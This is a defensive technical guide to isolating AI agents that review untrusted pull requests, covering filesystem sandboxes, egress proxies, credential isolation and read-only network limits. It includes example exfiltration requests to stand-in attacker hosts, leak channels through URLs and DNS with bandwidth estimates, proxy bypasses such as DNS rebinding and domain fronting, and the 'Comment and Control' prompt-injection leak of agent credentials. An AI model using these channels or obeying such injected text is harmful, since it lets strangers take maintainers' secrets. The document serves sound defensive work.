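GitHub mounts the virtual machine's entire disk read-only at `/host` inside the agent's container. It covers selected paths with empty tmpfs layers, so the agent sees empty directories there instead of the real contents. Then it starts the agent in a chroot, which makes `/host` the root of the file tree for that process. The agent finds every tool in its usual place but cannot change the installed copy.

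This design exposes everything by default and hides selected parts, so if a new tool stores a token in a directory that nobody thought to hide, the agent can read it. The bubblewrap command exposes only the paths it lists, which matches Saltzer and Schroeder's fail-safe rule. If someone forgets to list a path that the agent needs, the run fails visibly. GitHub's choice is easier to defend on a virtual machine set up for a single job than on a maintainer's laptop, where years of configuration files have accumulated.

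### Codex's protected paths

Codex has one of the more elaborate sandboxes among current coding agents. *Harness Engineering* (Barbaste, Darrigol and colleagues, 2026) compared the source code of eleven harnesses and used Codex as its example of the fullest safety design. Codex had policy rules, a model that reviews approval requests and an operating-system sandbox on three platforms. At the other end of the range, Mini-SWE-Agent had only limits on cost and steps.

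On Linux, Codex combines bubblewrap with seccomp. According to the *linux sandbox* README in OpenAI's code, Codex first mounts the whole disk read-only, then adds writable mounts for the directories where the agent may work, and finally mounts certain paths inside them read-only again. These protected paths include `.git`, where Git keeps a repository's history and settings, and `.codex`, which holds Codex's own configuration. In some checkouts, `.git` is a file that points to a directory elsewhere, which Codex also protects. If a protected path does not exist yet, Codex mounts the empty device `/dev/null` over its name so that the agent cannot create it.

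More specific rules override broader ones, so a project can make a repository writable, deny access to a directory inside it and restore access to one folder within that directory. This flexibility suits an agent that edits code, but the review agent in the example doesn't need it, because the simplest rule there is to make the entire source tree read-only.

Mounting the whole disk read-only still lets the agent read the maintainer's keys unless another rule denies access. *feat(linux-sandbox): support restricted ReadOnlyAccess in bwrap*, a change to Codex's source by viyatb-oai, added a second method that starts with an empty root and mounts only listed paths, so keys elsewhere on the disk are absent. OpenAI's documentation now includes a profile that denies access to the whole disk, then restores it for the project folder and a minimal set of system paths.

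The setting may not have worked everywhere. Duke University's *Introduction and Control Model* warns users that, as of April 2026, Codex could read almost anything on the computer regardless of their settings, contrary to the documentation. This is one institution's finding, with no published test, but a maintainer can check his own installation in a minute. Codex has a command that runs any program under its sandbox, and he can use it to try to read a harmless file outside the project.

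Codex's sandbox may fail inside a container that blocks the creation of namespaces. OpenAI then advises turning off the inner sandbox and using the container as the boundary. It warns that a malicious project could then send out anything available there, including the credentials for Codex, and limits this setup to trusted repositories. A pull request from an unknown contributor does not meet that condition, even if the repository is trustworthy.

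### Claude Code's shell sandbox and its file tools

Claude Code also uses bubblewrap on Linux and Seatbelt on macOS, but by default it sandboxes only shell commands and every program they start. The built-in tools for reading, editing and writing files run outside the sandbox, in the harness process, where Claude Code's permission rules govern them. MCP servers and hooks (commands that the harness runs at set moments) also run outside the sandbox.

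In the example, a steered agent might try to read a key with the shell command `cat`. If the sandbox denies the path, the command fails. The agent could then request the same file through the built-in reading tool, which the operating-system boundary does not control. Anthropic merges the paths from sandbox settings and permission rules into one sandbox configuration. This makes the two easier to keep consistent, but two different mechanisms still enforce them.

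The defaults also suit an agent that edits code better than one that reviews it. Shell commands can write to the working directory and read almost the entire disk, including `~/.ssh` and the file where Amazon's cloud tools store credentials. In the example, a maintainer would have to deny reads of the home directory, allow reads of the project directory again and make the source tree unwritable.

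Anthropic says the shell sandbox alone is not enough for fully unattended runs. Its separate sandbox runtime puts the same kind of boundary around the entire Claude Code process, including file tools, MCP servers and hooks. The bubblewrap command above also covers the whole process, because it starts the harness inside the sandbox. A third option is to run everything inside a container or a virtual machine.

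Even when the harness runs inside the sandbox, it needs to write to its own configuration directory. A steered session could leave a hook or a permission rule there, and Claude Code would load it the next time it started, perhaps outside any sandbox. The runtime blocks some of these paths automatically, and Anthropic tells users to deny the others. The launcher in the example gives every run a fresh home directory in memory, so nothing the agent leaves there reaches a later run.

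Nesting one sandbox in another can weaken the inner one. Bubblewrap cannot mount a new `/proc` in a container without special rights. For this case, Claude Code offers a weaker mode that reuses the container's existing `/proc` and so exposes information about the container's other processes. Anthropic recommends that mode only if the outer container already provides the isolation the user needs.

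File and network limits depend on each other, as Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) argues. An agent with an open network can send out any secret it can read, and an agent that can change system files may give itself a network connection. Anthropic also reports that sandboxing cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. This vendor figure counts prompts, not attacks, but it is relevant to Potiuk's worry about prompt fatigue because limiting what a command can reach removes much of the reason to ask for approval.

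### Sandlock's kernel rules and supervisor

The bubblewrap command fixes its rules before the agent starts, but some useful rules depend on facts that appear only during the run, such as the address a program connects to. Wang and Zheng designed Sandlock to handle both cases. It gives the kernel the rules that can be decided in advance, and sends only the kinds of system call that can't be decided that way to a supervisor, a trusted program outside the sandbox.

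Landlock enforces the lists of readable and writable paths and the permitted TCP ports. Seccomp refuses the system calls that Sandlock always forbids. For a rule about a particular host, seccomp pauses the call and notifies the supervisor, which then works as follows:

1. It copies the destination address from the program's memory once.
2. It compares the copy with the allowlist.
3. If the address is permitted, it makes the connection itself, using a duplicate of the program's socket and its own copy of the address.

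In the third step, the supervisor makes the connection using the copy of the address it checked, so the address cannot change after the check. If the supervisor only approved the original call, the kernel would read the address from the program's memory again, and another thread could have replaced it by then. Before Sandlock inspects the arguments of a newly started program, it freezes every task that could alter them, and it refuses the call if it cannot freeze them all.

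Wang and Zheng treat the start of a program as a signal and do not use those arguments to block programs, because an attacker can rename a program or write another that does the same thing. Command patterns have the same weakness. When the test runner starts, the supervisor can withdraw network access for the rest of the run, and the kernel and the supervisor then enforce the tighter rule whatever the program is named.

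Sandlock needs neither administrator rights nor a container image, but its supervisor is additional code that must be correct. Its developers, Wang and Zheng, checked ten cases, including reads outside the permitted paths, connections to unlisted hosts and attempts to exceed memory and process limits. All ten behaved as the policy required, but Wang and Zheng were confirming expected behaviour, not trying to break the tool. They also say that Sandlock's resource limits suit buggy code better than hostile code, for which cgroups remain stronger.

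### Running the contributor's tests

If the agent runs the contributor's test, the operating-system limits still apply to the test. Codex's sandbox, for instance, covers test runners and package managers that the agent starts, and the kernel enforces the limits even if a command has a misleading name. Running the test in the agent's own sandbox is still a problem, because the test then shares resources with the agent.

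With the command above, the test could write to `/work/out` and replace the agent's review. It could also kill the agent, which runs under the same user, or use the agent's connection to the model service. The contributor's code could do all of this directly, without prompt injection.

The tests therefore belong in a second sandbox with no connection to the model and no access to the review. They often have to write files next to the source code, which a read-only mount prevents. Bubblewrap can instead lay a temporary writable layer over the source:

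```bash
--overlay-src "$run/source" --tmp-overlay /work/source
```

These options replace the read-only mount of the source in the second sandbox. Test programs can then create or change files there, but the changes stay in memory and are discarded at the end, so the reviewer's source tree remains as the launcher prepared it.

A trusted program captures the test output, limits its size and gives it to the reviewer as another input file. Sandlock's pipelines support the same division, with different rules for each stage. Wang and Zheng point out that such a pipeline limits what each stage can do but not what it writes. The test can still print a sentence aimed at the model, so the reviewer has to treat the log as untrusted text.

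Many tests also need packages from the internet. Codex's cloud service has a setup phase with network access, followed by an agent phase that is offline by default. OpenAI makes secrets available during setup and removes them before the agent starts. This protects against the agent but not against a contributor who changes the dependency list or an installation script, because those changes would take effect during setup. A safer launcher installs only the packages the main branch requires and reports any test that needs a new package as not run.

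A separate virtual machine is worth the trouble if a project regularly runs strangers' tests. An attacker can use a test to look for a flaw in the kernel by making any system call the filter permits, in any order, whereas a reviewer that only reads code mostly uses ordinary kernel functions through known tools.

### Local sockets and the Docker daemon

Programs on the same machine often communicate through Unix sockets, which usually appear as files. A network namespace does not stop a sandboxed process from connecting to a socket whose file it can see. Neither does a read-only mount, because connecting to a socket does not change the filesystem. In one of ArchWiki's *Bubblewrap examples*, a sandboxed program uses the desktop's display socket through a read-only mount.

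Among common sockets, Docker's is the most dangerous. It gives access to the Docker daemon, the background program that manages containers. The daemon normally runs with administrator rights and will start a container with any host directory mounted in it. An agent that can send it requests can therefore read or change the whole disk, even though the agent's own process stays in its sandbox. Anthropic says allowing this socket effectively grants access to the host. OpenAI calls such sockets an escape hatch for tools like Docker and tells users to open them sparingly.

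Other services pose the same risk. bubblewrap's documentation warns that a program may gain rights through anything mounted into the sandbox, such as the socket of D-Bus, the message system that Linux desktop programs use to control one another. On Windows, the Linux subsystem WSL2 starts Windows programs through a Unix socket, so Claude Code's sandbox blocks that route.

In the example, the sockets are absent because the command never mounts the directories that contain them. A sandbox that mounts the entire disk has to block connections to them some other way. On Linux, Claude Code uses a seccomp filter. The filter is optional, so a maintainer has to confirm that it is installed. GitHub keeps the Docker socket away from the agent and connects it to the trusted gateway that starts the tool servers.

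Some projects have tests that start their own containers. Mounting the host's Docker socket would let those tests run, but it would also give the contributor control of the host. Such tests need a virtual machine with a separate Docker daemon, as in Docker's own sandbox product.

### Git hooks and other files that run later

A file that the agent writes can do harm after the sandbox has closed. Git runs scripts called hooks when someone commits or switches branches, and its configuration can specify other programs to run. An agent that can write to `.git` can therefore add a hook or setting that runs code when the maintainer next uses Git in that checkout, outside the sandbox and with the maintainer's permissions. OpenAI gives the same warning about build scripts, package-manager hooks and shell startup files.

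Codex protects the whole `.git` directory, while Claude Code's sandbox runtime denies writes to the hooks and configuration at the project root. On macOS, the runtime checks each write as it happens, so the rule also covers repositories created during the session. On Linux, it lists the protected paths once at launch, so it misses repositories that the agent creates later. It also searches for nested repositories only to a shallow depth. Anthropic therefore tells users to review new files after an unattended run on Linux.

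The read-only source tree in the example prevents the agent from changing the existing hooks and configuration. The agent could still create a new Git repository in `/work/out` with its own settings. If the publisher later ran Git in that directory, Git might apply those settings while it had access to the publisher's credentials. The publisher should read the output as plain files and never run tools in that directory.

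A read-only mount does not protect the agent from harmful settings in the pull request, because the contributor made those changes before the mount. Git doesn't copy hooks or local configuration from a contributor's repository, but a harness may read settings from ordinary project files, such as `.mcp.json` or those in the `.claude` directory, which a contributor can add or change. The command therefore starts the agent in its empty home directory instead of the source tree. The launcher should also turn off the harness's project settings or load them from the main branch, and leave the contributor's copies in the diff as text to review.

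## Read-only network access

The sandbox built so far has no network connection, so the agent cannot reach its model. A launcher that opens a connection should keep it read-only. Maintainers use "read-only" for three different limits: the agent can contact only certain hosts, it can send only requests that aren't meant to change anything on the server, or it can use only a credential without write permission.

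The limit on requests relies on the HTTP method, the part of every web request that indicates its purpose. GET fetches something, HEAD fetches only the headers that would accompany it, and OPTIONS checks which methods the server accepts. The HTTP standard defines all three as safe, meaning that the client does not request a change on the server. Methods such as POST and DELETE can create, change or remove things there.

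Each row below gives a request that an injected agent could still make if the launcher had set only one of the limits.

| Only limit in place | Request that still succeeds | Result |
|---|---|---|
| Listed hosts | `POST https://api.github.com/repos/example/library/issues/17/comments` | A public comment, if the agent's token can write |
| GET, HEAD and OPTIONS | `GET https://collector.example/?d=...` | Private text reaches a stranger's server inside the address |
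| Read-only token | `POST https://paste.example/` | A private file appears on a site that needs no token |

A read-only token would stop the comment, and a host list would stop the other two requests. The method limit is still useful with both in place. A stranger can put his own token in the pull request, and an injected agent could use it to upload private text to the stranger's account on a listed host unless the sandbox blocks POST.

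Limiting the agent to read-only HTTP methods such as GET prevents changes only if servers treat those requests as read-only. Some websites confirm a subscription or start a job when someone opens a link, which sends a GET request. A short list of allowed hosts keeps the agent away from most of these sites.

### The route from the sandbox to a host

Suppose the description of the example pull request mentions an older issue, and the agent wants to read it. The request takes the following route:

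1. The agent starts an ordinary program such as `curl`. The sandbox has an empty network namespace, so a direct connection to any outside address fails.
2. An environment variable tells the program to use a proxy at a local address. A small forwarder inside the sandbox listens there and copies everything to a Unix socket that the launcher has mounted.
3. The egress proxy listens on that socket from outside the sandbox. The program asks it for a connection to `api.github.com`.
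4. The proxy compares the name with its allowlist and refuses the request if the name is missing.
5. The proxy looks up the host's network address, checks it and opens the onward connection itself.

In the bubblewrap command, this takes two more options, placed before `--remount-ro /`:

```bash
--ro-bind "$run/egress.sock" /run/egress.sock  # the only way out
--setenv HTTPS_PROXY http://127.0.0.1:3128     # local address of the forwarder
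```

A short script inside the sandbox then starts the forwarder and the agent:

```bash
socat TCP-LISTEN:3128,bind=127.0.0.1,fork UNIX-CONNECT:/run/egress.sock &
exec /usr/bin/review-agent
```

*Aegis OS* (Zhao, 2026) describes a runtime for coding agents that also connects bubblewrap to its proxy through a Unix socket, and adds a token that the sandboxed side must present.

The environment variable only helps programs find the proxy. A program that ignores it gets no connection. In a forum thread, *Codex internet access not working*, a user's tests failed because the network was unreachable, and another user replied that requests from Node, a JavaScript runtime, had to use the proxy variable. This failure is annoying but safe, because if the sandbox had an ordinary route to the internet, the same program would have bypassed the proxy, perhaps without anyone noticing.

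Codex users can give commands unrestricted direct network access by accident, because Codex has separate settings for network access and the proxy. According to OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security*, this happens when the network is on and the proxy is off. The proxy is off by default. Claude Code's shell sandbox always uses a proxy, but according to Anthropic's *Sandboxing*, a request for a new host normally prompts the user. Nobody can answer that prompt when a reviewer runs unattended, so its maintainer should choose the setting that blocks unlisted hosts automatically.

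The host list should contain exact names where possible. In Codex, `*.example.com` permits every subdomain, including ones that the owner creates later or rents to customers. OpenAI notes that a domain rule does not show whether the permitted host is trustworthy.

The proxy also has to check the address that a domain name resolves to, because the name's owner can point it anywhere. It could point to the administration page of the maintainer's router or, on a rented cloud machine, to the internal service that issues credentials. Codex blocks a name that resolves to a local or private address even if the name is on the allowlist.

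An attacker who controls a host name can still return a public address when the proxy checks the name and a private one when the proxy connects. This attack is called DNS rebinding, where DNS is the system that translates host names into addresses. OpenAI says that its check reduces the risk but doesn't eliminate it, because that would require the proxy to connect to the same address it checked.

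Wang and Zheng's Sandlock resolves every listed hostname once, when the sandbox starts, and then permits only those addresses. It therefore can't support wildcard names, and a connection may fail if a service moves to a new address during the run. Reviews rarely last long enough for an address change to matter. ClawSweeper, for example, limits each review to ten minutes.

### What a proxy sees of an encrypted request

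Code hosts generally require HTTPS, which is HTTP encrypted with TLS. To send an HTTPS request through a proxy, a program first sends a CONNECT request with the host name and port. The proxy connects to that host and copies encrypted bytes in both directions. It can see the host name, the amount of data and the timing, but not the method, path, headers or content.

A host list works without decryption, and Anthropic built Claude Code's proxy this way. To such a proxy, reading an issue on GitHub and posting a comment there are both just connections to `api.github.com`. A proxy that filters by method or path must terminate TLS, which means that it takes the server's place at the end of the encrypted connection:

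1. The proxy creates a certificate in the host's name and signs it with its own certificate authority (CA), an issuer that vouches for certificates.
2. The program in the sandbox accepts this certificate because the launcher has installed the CA's own certificate there.
3. The proxy decrypts the request and applies its rules.
4. If the rules permit the request, the proxy sends it over a second encrypted connection to the real server, after verifying that server's certificate.

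Anyone who gets the CA's private key can impersonate any website to a program that trusts the CA. The launcher should therefore create a new CA for each run, keep the private key outside the sandbox and never install the certificate in the maintainer's browser or system settings. Codex keeps the certificate and the key in its configuration directory, so a sandbox that exposes the whole disk may expose the key.

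TLS termination also causes practical problems. Programs keep separate lists of trusted CAs, so the launcher may have to set `SSL_CERT_FILE` for some tools, `NODE_EXTRA_CA_CERTS` for Node and `GIT_SSL_CAINFO` for Git. A program that accepts only one particular certificate will fail to connect. The proxy can also read every token and message that passes through it, which makes a flaw in the proxy more serious. These drawbacks are worth accepting if the list of allowed hosts includes one like GitHub, where anyone can open an account.

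A proxy that filters requests by method must check every request, because one encrypted connection can carry many. It should refuse a body on a GET request, because a reader has no use for one. It should also refuse to switch a connection to WebSocket, a protocol for live updates that begins with a GET request but then can carry any data in both directions.

If the rules cover paths, the proxy must also convert each path to a standard form before comparing it. Otherwise, `..` segments or encoded characters could make a forbidden path look like a permitted one. Zhao's proxy does this.

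When the whole harness runs inside the sandbox, as in the example, its connection to the model needs an exception because sending a prompt takes a POST request. The proxy should permit POST only to the one model-service path that the harness uses. Codex does not need this exception because its method limit applies to the commands that the agent starts, not to the harness's own connection to the model.

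### Codex's limited mode

Codex's network proxy has a `limited` mode that restricts commands to the three safe methods, GET, HEAD and OPTIONS. OpenAI's *Configuration Reference* lists the `limited` and `full` modes but does not explain them. OpenAI's *codex-network-proxy* (2026), the documentation that accompanies the source code, describes limited mode as intended for read-only access. The mode also blocks SOCKS5, a proxy protocol that forwards connections without checking HTTP methods.

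In January 2026, OpenAI blocked all HTTPS connections in limited mode because they would have bypassed the method check. On 24 February, it added TLS termination under the setting `mitm`, short for "man in the middle". The proxy now allows HTTPS in limited mode only if `mitm` is on. Neither setting is on by default, since the mode defaults to `full` and `mitm` defaults to `false`.

A later passage in the same document contradicts this, describing HTTPS in limited mode as a tunnel without method checks. That passage is probably out of date, since OpenAI added TLS termination and the new rule for HTTPS connections in one change. But HTTPS is the case that matters here, so a maintainer should test the installed version by sending a harmless POST over HTTPS to a listed host. The request should fail with error 403 and the header `x-proxy-error: blocked-by-method-policy`.

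With the setting names from OpenAI's documentation, a profile for the example could look like this:

```toml
default_permissions = "review"

[features]
network_proxy = true              # start the proxy

[permissions.review.filesystem]
":minimal" = "read"               # only basic system paths

[permissions.review.filesystem.":workspace_roots"]
"." = "read"                      # source tree, read-only

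[permissions.review.network]
enabled = true
mode = "limited"                  # GET, HEAD and OPTIONS
mitm = true                       # decrypt HTTPS to check the method

[permissions.review.network.domains]
"api.github.com" = "allow"
```

Permission profiles are still in beta, so the names may change.

Programs that embed the proxy can add a function that allows requests to hosts missing from the allowlist, though it cannot override an explicit prohibition. OpenAI's example approves any request from a command starting with `curl`, assuming the user has already approved such commands. A reviewer's launcher should leave this function out, because the agent writes the command and could choose which hosts to reach.

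Codex's cloud service can optionally restrict requests to the same three methods. OpenAI's *Agent internet access* presents this option as an addition to the list of permitted domains.

### ClawSweeper's review profile

ClawSweeper combines all three limits when it reviews with Codex. Its profile allows access to GitHub, npm (the main registry for JavaScript packages), Node, MDN's web documentation and OpenClaw's own documentation. The proxy decrypts HTTPS and accepts only GET, HEAD and OPTIONS requests. Any GitHub token the job supplies is read-only and expires within the hour. OpenClaw also fetches context for the review in advance, which the agent can use when it has no token.

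This list suits OpenClaw, which is written largely for Node, because a reviewer may have to check whether a function exists or what a package contains. A reviewer of a C library would need a different list, perhaps with only the model service on it.

OpenClaw tells the agent that a blocked request is not evidence against a pull request. Without this instruction, an agent that could not open a link might conclude that the contributor had invented it. Relying on the model to follow the instruction does no harm, because the instruction affects only the quality of the review.

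OpenClaw also instructs the agent never to put the token in a URL or send it to a host other than GitHub. The method and host limits it describes would not block a GET request to npm with the token in the URL. The damage would be small, because npm would be the recipient and the token is read-only and short-lived. But OpenClaw describes no other protection for this case, and a proxy that added the token to GitHub requests itself would make the instruction unnecessary.

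### Git and GraphQL reads that use POST

A filter that blocks all POST requests breaks `git fetch` over HTTPS. Git first sends a GET request to get the server's list of branches and tags, then lists the commits it needs in one or more POST requests, because that list can be too long for a URL. A push follows the same pattern, but its POST goes to a path ending in `git-receive-pack` instead of `git-upload-pack`. The names describe the transfer from the server's side.

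A proxy that terminates TLS can therefore permit one more request:

```text
POST https://github.com/example/library.git/git-upload-pack
```

This rule lets the agent fetch from one repository and blocks every push. If the rule matched only the end of the path, the agent could fetch any public repository on GitHub, including one in which a stranger has left further instructions.

The example review doesn't need the exception, because the launcher fetches the source before the agent starts. If the agent has to find out when a line last changed, the launcher can fetch more of the history. GitHub also provides repository snapshots through GET requests, but these contain no history.

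GraphQL is harder to filter because queries and mutations differ only in the body of the request. Searching the body for the word "mutation" is unreliable because the word can appear in ordinary text. A body can also define several operations and use a separate field to select the one to run. OpenAI has added hooks to Codex's proxy that match a request's method, path, query string and headers. They do not match the body, so they cannot distinguish a GraphQL read from a write.

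The simplest alternative to GraphQL is GitHub's older REST API, which uses GET for reads and covers issues, comments and diffs. `gh` commands that use GraphQL will fail under a filter like ClawSweeper's, but `gh api` can send GET requests to the REST API.

A project that needs GraphQL can use a read-only relay, a small trusted program outside the sandbox that stores a few complete queries, such as one that returns a pull request's review threads. The agent names the query and supplies the pull request's number. The relay checks that the value is numeric, inserts it into the query and sends the POST request. The agent never writes GraphQL, so it can't turn the request into a mutation. Magpie's `vetted-op-read` uses the same idea for commands.

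Another narrow exception is to permit POST requests to the GraphQL path only with a read-only token that the proxy attaches, so that the code host refuses mutations. The proxy has to remove any token the agent supplies, because a stranger's token would otherwise let the agent run mutations in the stranger's account.

### Package registries and shared hosts

Installing packages requires access to more hosts than reviewing code does. A package manager may contact a registry, a separate download server and the code hosts of individual packages. OpenAI's preset list for Codex's cloud service contains 71 domains for common dependencies, including `github.com`, `gitlab.com`, `sourceforge.net`, `google.com` and `azure.com`. The companies that own these five domains let outsiders publish or store material on some of their services. The list may be reasonable for building software, but a review agent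 that uses it can reach many places where a stranger could leave instructions or collect data.

For the tests, the launcher can install the main branch's packages before the agent starts. If the set of packages is too large or changes too often, the project can run a mirror, a server that keeps copies of packages, and allow the agent to connect only to that server. The mirror should serve only packages on an approved list. If it forwarded every request to the public registry, an agent compromised by prompt injection could still send a message out through the names of the packages it requested.

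A single permitted host can cause the same problem when it serves many customers. On GitHub, for example, the project's repository and the attacker's share a hostname. Wang and Zheng note that an agent allowed to contact a model service's network address may also reach an attacker's endpoint behind that address. They conclude that useful rules often have to cover the request's method, host and path.

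In the example, the proxy could permit only GET requests under `/repos/example/library/` on `api.github.com`. The agent could then read the older issue but not a page in the attacker's repository. GitHub redirects snapshot requests to another host. The proxy should check the redirected request like any other, so the download fails until the maintainer also lists that host and path.

Zhao's proxy ties each credential to a domain, method and path prefix, and adds it only to requests that match all three. Zhao tested Aegis OS with 80 attacks in eight categories, one of which was abuse of a permitted domain. All the attacks succeeded without the protections, and none succeeded with them. Switching off any component let the attacks in its category succeed again. The results show that each component has an effect, but they are weak evidence about attacks Zhao did not think of, because Zhao designed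 both the system and the tests, and the attack categories correspond to the system's components.

Domain fronting can get past a proxy that checks only host names. It relies on large delivery networks that serve many websites from the same machines. The program connects through the proxy to a permitted website on such a network, then requests a different one inside the encrypted connection, where the proxy can't read the name. Anthropic warns that this may work against Claude Code's built-in proxy and recommends that users who need a stronger guarantee use a custom proxy that terminates TLS.

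That proxy must compare the name inside each decrypted request with the name it approved, and refuse the request if they differ. If a tool cannot work with the proxy's certificate, the launcher can fetch what the tool would have fetched, or the review can go ahead without it. The maintainer should not weaken the rule for that tool.

Fetching in advance moves the risk to the launcher, which runs outside the sandbox and may have more access, so it must not open a link just because a stranger included it. ClawSweeper downloads images and videos that contributors attach as proof that a change works, but OpenClaw does not let the patch text supply the addresses for these downloads. A launcher can follow the same rule by building addresses from the repository name and pull request number.

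### Data in permitted requests

A read-only connection can still leak data, because a request carries information to the server even if it changes nothing there. *A Note on the Confinement Problem* (Lampson, 1973) describes a customer who runs somebody else's program on private data, and lists three ways the data can get out: storage that others can read, legitimate channels such as the bill for the service, and covert channels such as the program's effect on the machine's load.

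In these terms, the address of a GET request is a legitimate channel. The agent needs it to name a page, but an agent compromised by prompt injection can add other text to it. A DNS lookup can also carry text, because the name is sent to the server responsible for its domain. If the agent looks up a name under an attacker's domain, the attacker receives whatever the name contains, even if a firewall blocks the connection that would follow.

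A few hundred requests can carry a lot of data. Addresses can safely use at least 64 different characters, so each character carries 6 bits and 2,000 characters carry 1,500 bytes. DNS does not distinguish capital from small letters, so a set of 32 characters is convenient, and each carries 5 bits. A DNS name can have about 250 characters, of which perhaps 200 are free for data. The third row of the table assumes that the proxy permits only a fixed list of 1,024 complete addresses. The agent can then send 10 bits per request through its choice of address, because 2^10 = 1,024.

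| What the agent can choose | Data per request | Data in 300 requests |
|---|---|---|
| 2,000 characters of a GET address | 1,500 bytes | 450,000 bytes |
| 200 characters of a DNS name | 125 bytes | 37,500 bytes |
| One of 1,024 fixed addresses | 10 bits | 375 bytes |

A 40-character token fits into a single DNS lookup, and even the fixed addresses could carry nine such tokens. The 450,000 bytes in the first row could hold a novel of about 75,000 words or many confidential security reports.

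These figures assume that the attacker can see the requests. If every request goes to GitHub's servers under the project's paths, the text ends up in GitHub's logs, where a stranger normally can't read it. The risk is much higher if the permitted paths include a page with statistics that the attacker can view, such as the download count of his own package. A host list therefore reduces the number of possible recipients, while limits on addresses and requests reduce the amount of data that can leak.

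Lampson's remedy, which he called masking, was to let the customer determine what the program puts into each channel. For the reviewer, the launcher and the proxy should therefore decide as much of each request as possible.

The proxy should do all DNS lookups, and only after it has found the name on the allowlist, because the lookup itself can carry data out. The sandbox in the example has no route to a DNS server, so its programs have to send the name to the proxy. Sandlock goes further and looks up the listed names before the agent starts. A DNS filter that blocks only known bad domains is not enough, because an attacker can register a new one.

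For HTTP, the proxy should allow only fixed paths, remove query strings that the page doesn't need, and replace the agent's headers with its own. A relay does all of this automatically, because it builds the request from a few checked values. Scanning requests for known tokens is a weaker measure. It can catch an agent that copies a token by mistake, but an attacker can have the agent encode the token first.

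The proxy should also cap the number of requests. With 20 requests instead of 300, an agent choosing among 1,024 addresses can send 25 bytes, which may still be a large part of a token. A contributor can start more runs by opening more pull requests, so the launcher needs to cap the runs that one person can trigger. Neither cap does much if the agent can write any address, because 20 addresses of 2,000 characters can still carry 30,000 bytes.

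A log of requests helps to detect misuse. Codex's proxy can record each request's host and method and whether the proxy allowed it. OpenAI deliberately leaves out the path and query string because they can contain private data, so the log can show an unusual number of requests but not an unusually long URL. A project's own proxy could record the URL's length without its text.

Some tools do not use the egress proxy. Codex's web search runs through OpenAI and by default returns pages from OpenAI's index instead of fetching them live. The agent still writes the search terms, and the results may contain text written by strangers. Codex switches to live results when the user gives it full access. A maintainer can turn web search off by setting `web_search = "disabled"`, and OpenClaw turns it off when ClawSweeper reviews a local branch.

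The connection to the model can carry out by far the most data, because the harness sends the model everything the agent reads. No cap on its traffic can prevent leaks. The proxy can only ensure that the data goes to the intended service and to the project's own account there. Which account receives the data depends on who supplies the key.

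## Keeping credentials out of the agent's reach

A credential is anything that lets a program act for an account, such as a password, a token, a private key, or a connection to another program that signs requests. The sandbox and egress proxy limit what the agent can do from the maintainer's machine, but a stranger who obtains a credential can use it from their own computer, where neither limit applies.

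### Where a process finds credentials

The last column shows how the example runtime closes each place that a steered agent might search.

| Place | What may be there | In the example |
|---|---|---|
| The agent's own environment | Keys and tokens from a login shell or build service | It starts empty |
| Other processes' environments, under `/proc` | The same values, kept by the programs that started the agent | The agent sees only the sandbox's processes |
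| Home directory | `~/.aws/credentials`, `~/.ssh`, `~/.netrc`, the login for `gh` | The home directory is empty |
| Git configuration | A token saved for later Git commands | The launcher leaves it out of the source copy |
| SSH and GPG agent sockets | Access to unlocked keys | The launcher never mounts them |
| Cloud metadata address | Temporary credentials for the machine's cloud role | The machine has no role, and the proxy refuses the address |
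| Logs | Tokens that an earlier step printed | The launcher never mounts them |
| The harness | The key for the model service | The proxy holds the key |

GitHub's standard step for fetching code, `actions/checkout`, saves the job's token so that later Git commands can use it. Up to version 5, it writes the token to `.git/config` inside the checkout, where a reviewing agent can read it even through a read-only mount. Version 6 writes it to a separate file on the same machine. In all these versions, setting `persist-credentials: false` prevents the step from saving the token.

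SSH and GPG agents, which are unrelated to AI agents, are small programs that hold unlocked keys and sign whatever a connected program submits, so a process can misuse a key without ever reading it.

If a rented cloud machine has a role in the customer's account, any program on it can get temporary credentials from a fixed address, usually 169.254.169.254. OpenClaw checks rented Amazon machines for such a role before it sets up a worker on them. Renting a machine without a role is safer than blocking the address, because the address then has no credentials to provide.

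### Starting from an empty environment

Apache Magpie starts the harness through a wrapper called `claude-iso`. The wrapper uses `env -i`, which runs a program without any inherited environment variables, and then restores a short list: `HOME`, `PATH`, `SHELL`, `TERM`, `LANG`, `XDG_*`, `DISPLAY`, `SSH_AUTH_SOCK`, `USER`, `LOGNAME` and `PWD`. Because it restores only these variables by default, it also drops any new token a maintainer later adds to their shell settings. A maintainer can let a token through for one session only by naming it in `CLAUDE_ISO_ALLOW`.

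Two of the restored variables point to credentials. `SSH_AUTH_SOCK` gives the location of the SSH agent's socket, and `HOME` gives the location of every credential file in the home directory. Magpie's sandbox hides most of that directory from shell commands but leaves `~/.config/gh` readable, because `gh` needs its token. Potiuk intends `gh` to use the token without the agent seeing it, so a permission rule stops the harness's own reading tool from opening the file. This prevents accidental disclosure through that tool, but a steered agent with a command line can still print the file, because shell commands in the sandbox can read it just as `gh` can.

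Giving the agent an empty environment also doesn't remove the copy of the credentials held by the process that started it. On Linux, a process can normally read the starting environment of any other process running under the same user. Removing a variable later does not reliably help, because the usual functions for doing so leave the old text in the startup memory that `/proc` exposes.

This affects the bubblewrap command too. `--clearenv` clears the variables for the agent, but bubblewrap keeps a helper process running inside the sandbox, and that process began with whatever environment the launcher passed to it. The launcher should therefore empty the environment before bubblewrap starts:

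```bash
env -i PATH=/usr/bin bwrap "${args[@]}" /usr/bin/review-agent
```

### Comment and Control

In April 2026, security engineer Aonan Guan showed what happens when a runtime filters only the agent's side. Working with Zhengyu Liu and Gavin Zhong of Johns Hopkins University, he used text in pull requests, issues and comments to make three vendors' agents on GitHub reveal credentials, a method he called "Comment and Control". The table combines information from SecurityWeek's *Claude Code, Gemini CLI, GitHub Copilot Agents Vulnerable to Prompt Injection* and Techzine's *AI agents on GitHub leak API keys via prompt injection*. CVSS is a common scale for the severity of security flaws, with a maximum of 10.

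| Agent | What it exposed | Where the values came out | Vendor's response |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code Security Review | Anthropic API key, GitHub token | Review comment or workflow log | Rated it critical (CVSS 9.4), paid $100, blocked the program `ps` |
| Gemini CLI Action | Gemini API key | Public issue comment | Paid $1,337, added instructions to the system prompt |
| GitHub Copilot Agent | Four credentials, including a GitHub token and a Copilot token | Git push | Paid $500, called it a known architectural limitation |

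GitHub had protected Copilot by removing sensitive variables from the shell that ran the agent's commands, scanning output for secrets and restricting network access with a firewall. But the shell could still read the full environment of the process that had started it. The scanner missed the secrets because the agent had encoded them, and the firewall allowed the push because it went to GitHub. This attack required a maintainer to assign the issue to Copilot, whereas the other two agents could start automatically.

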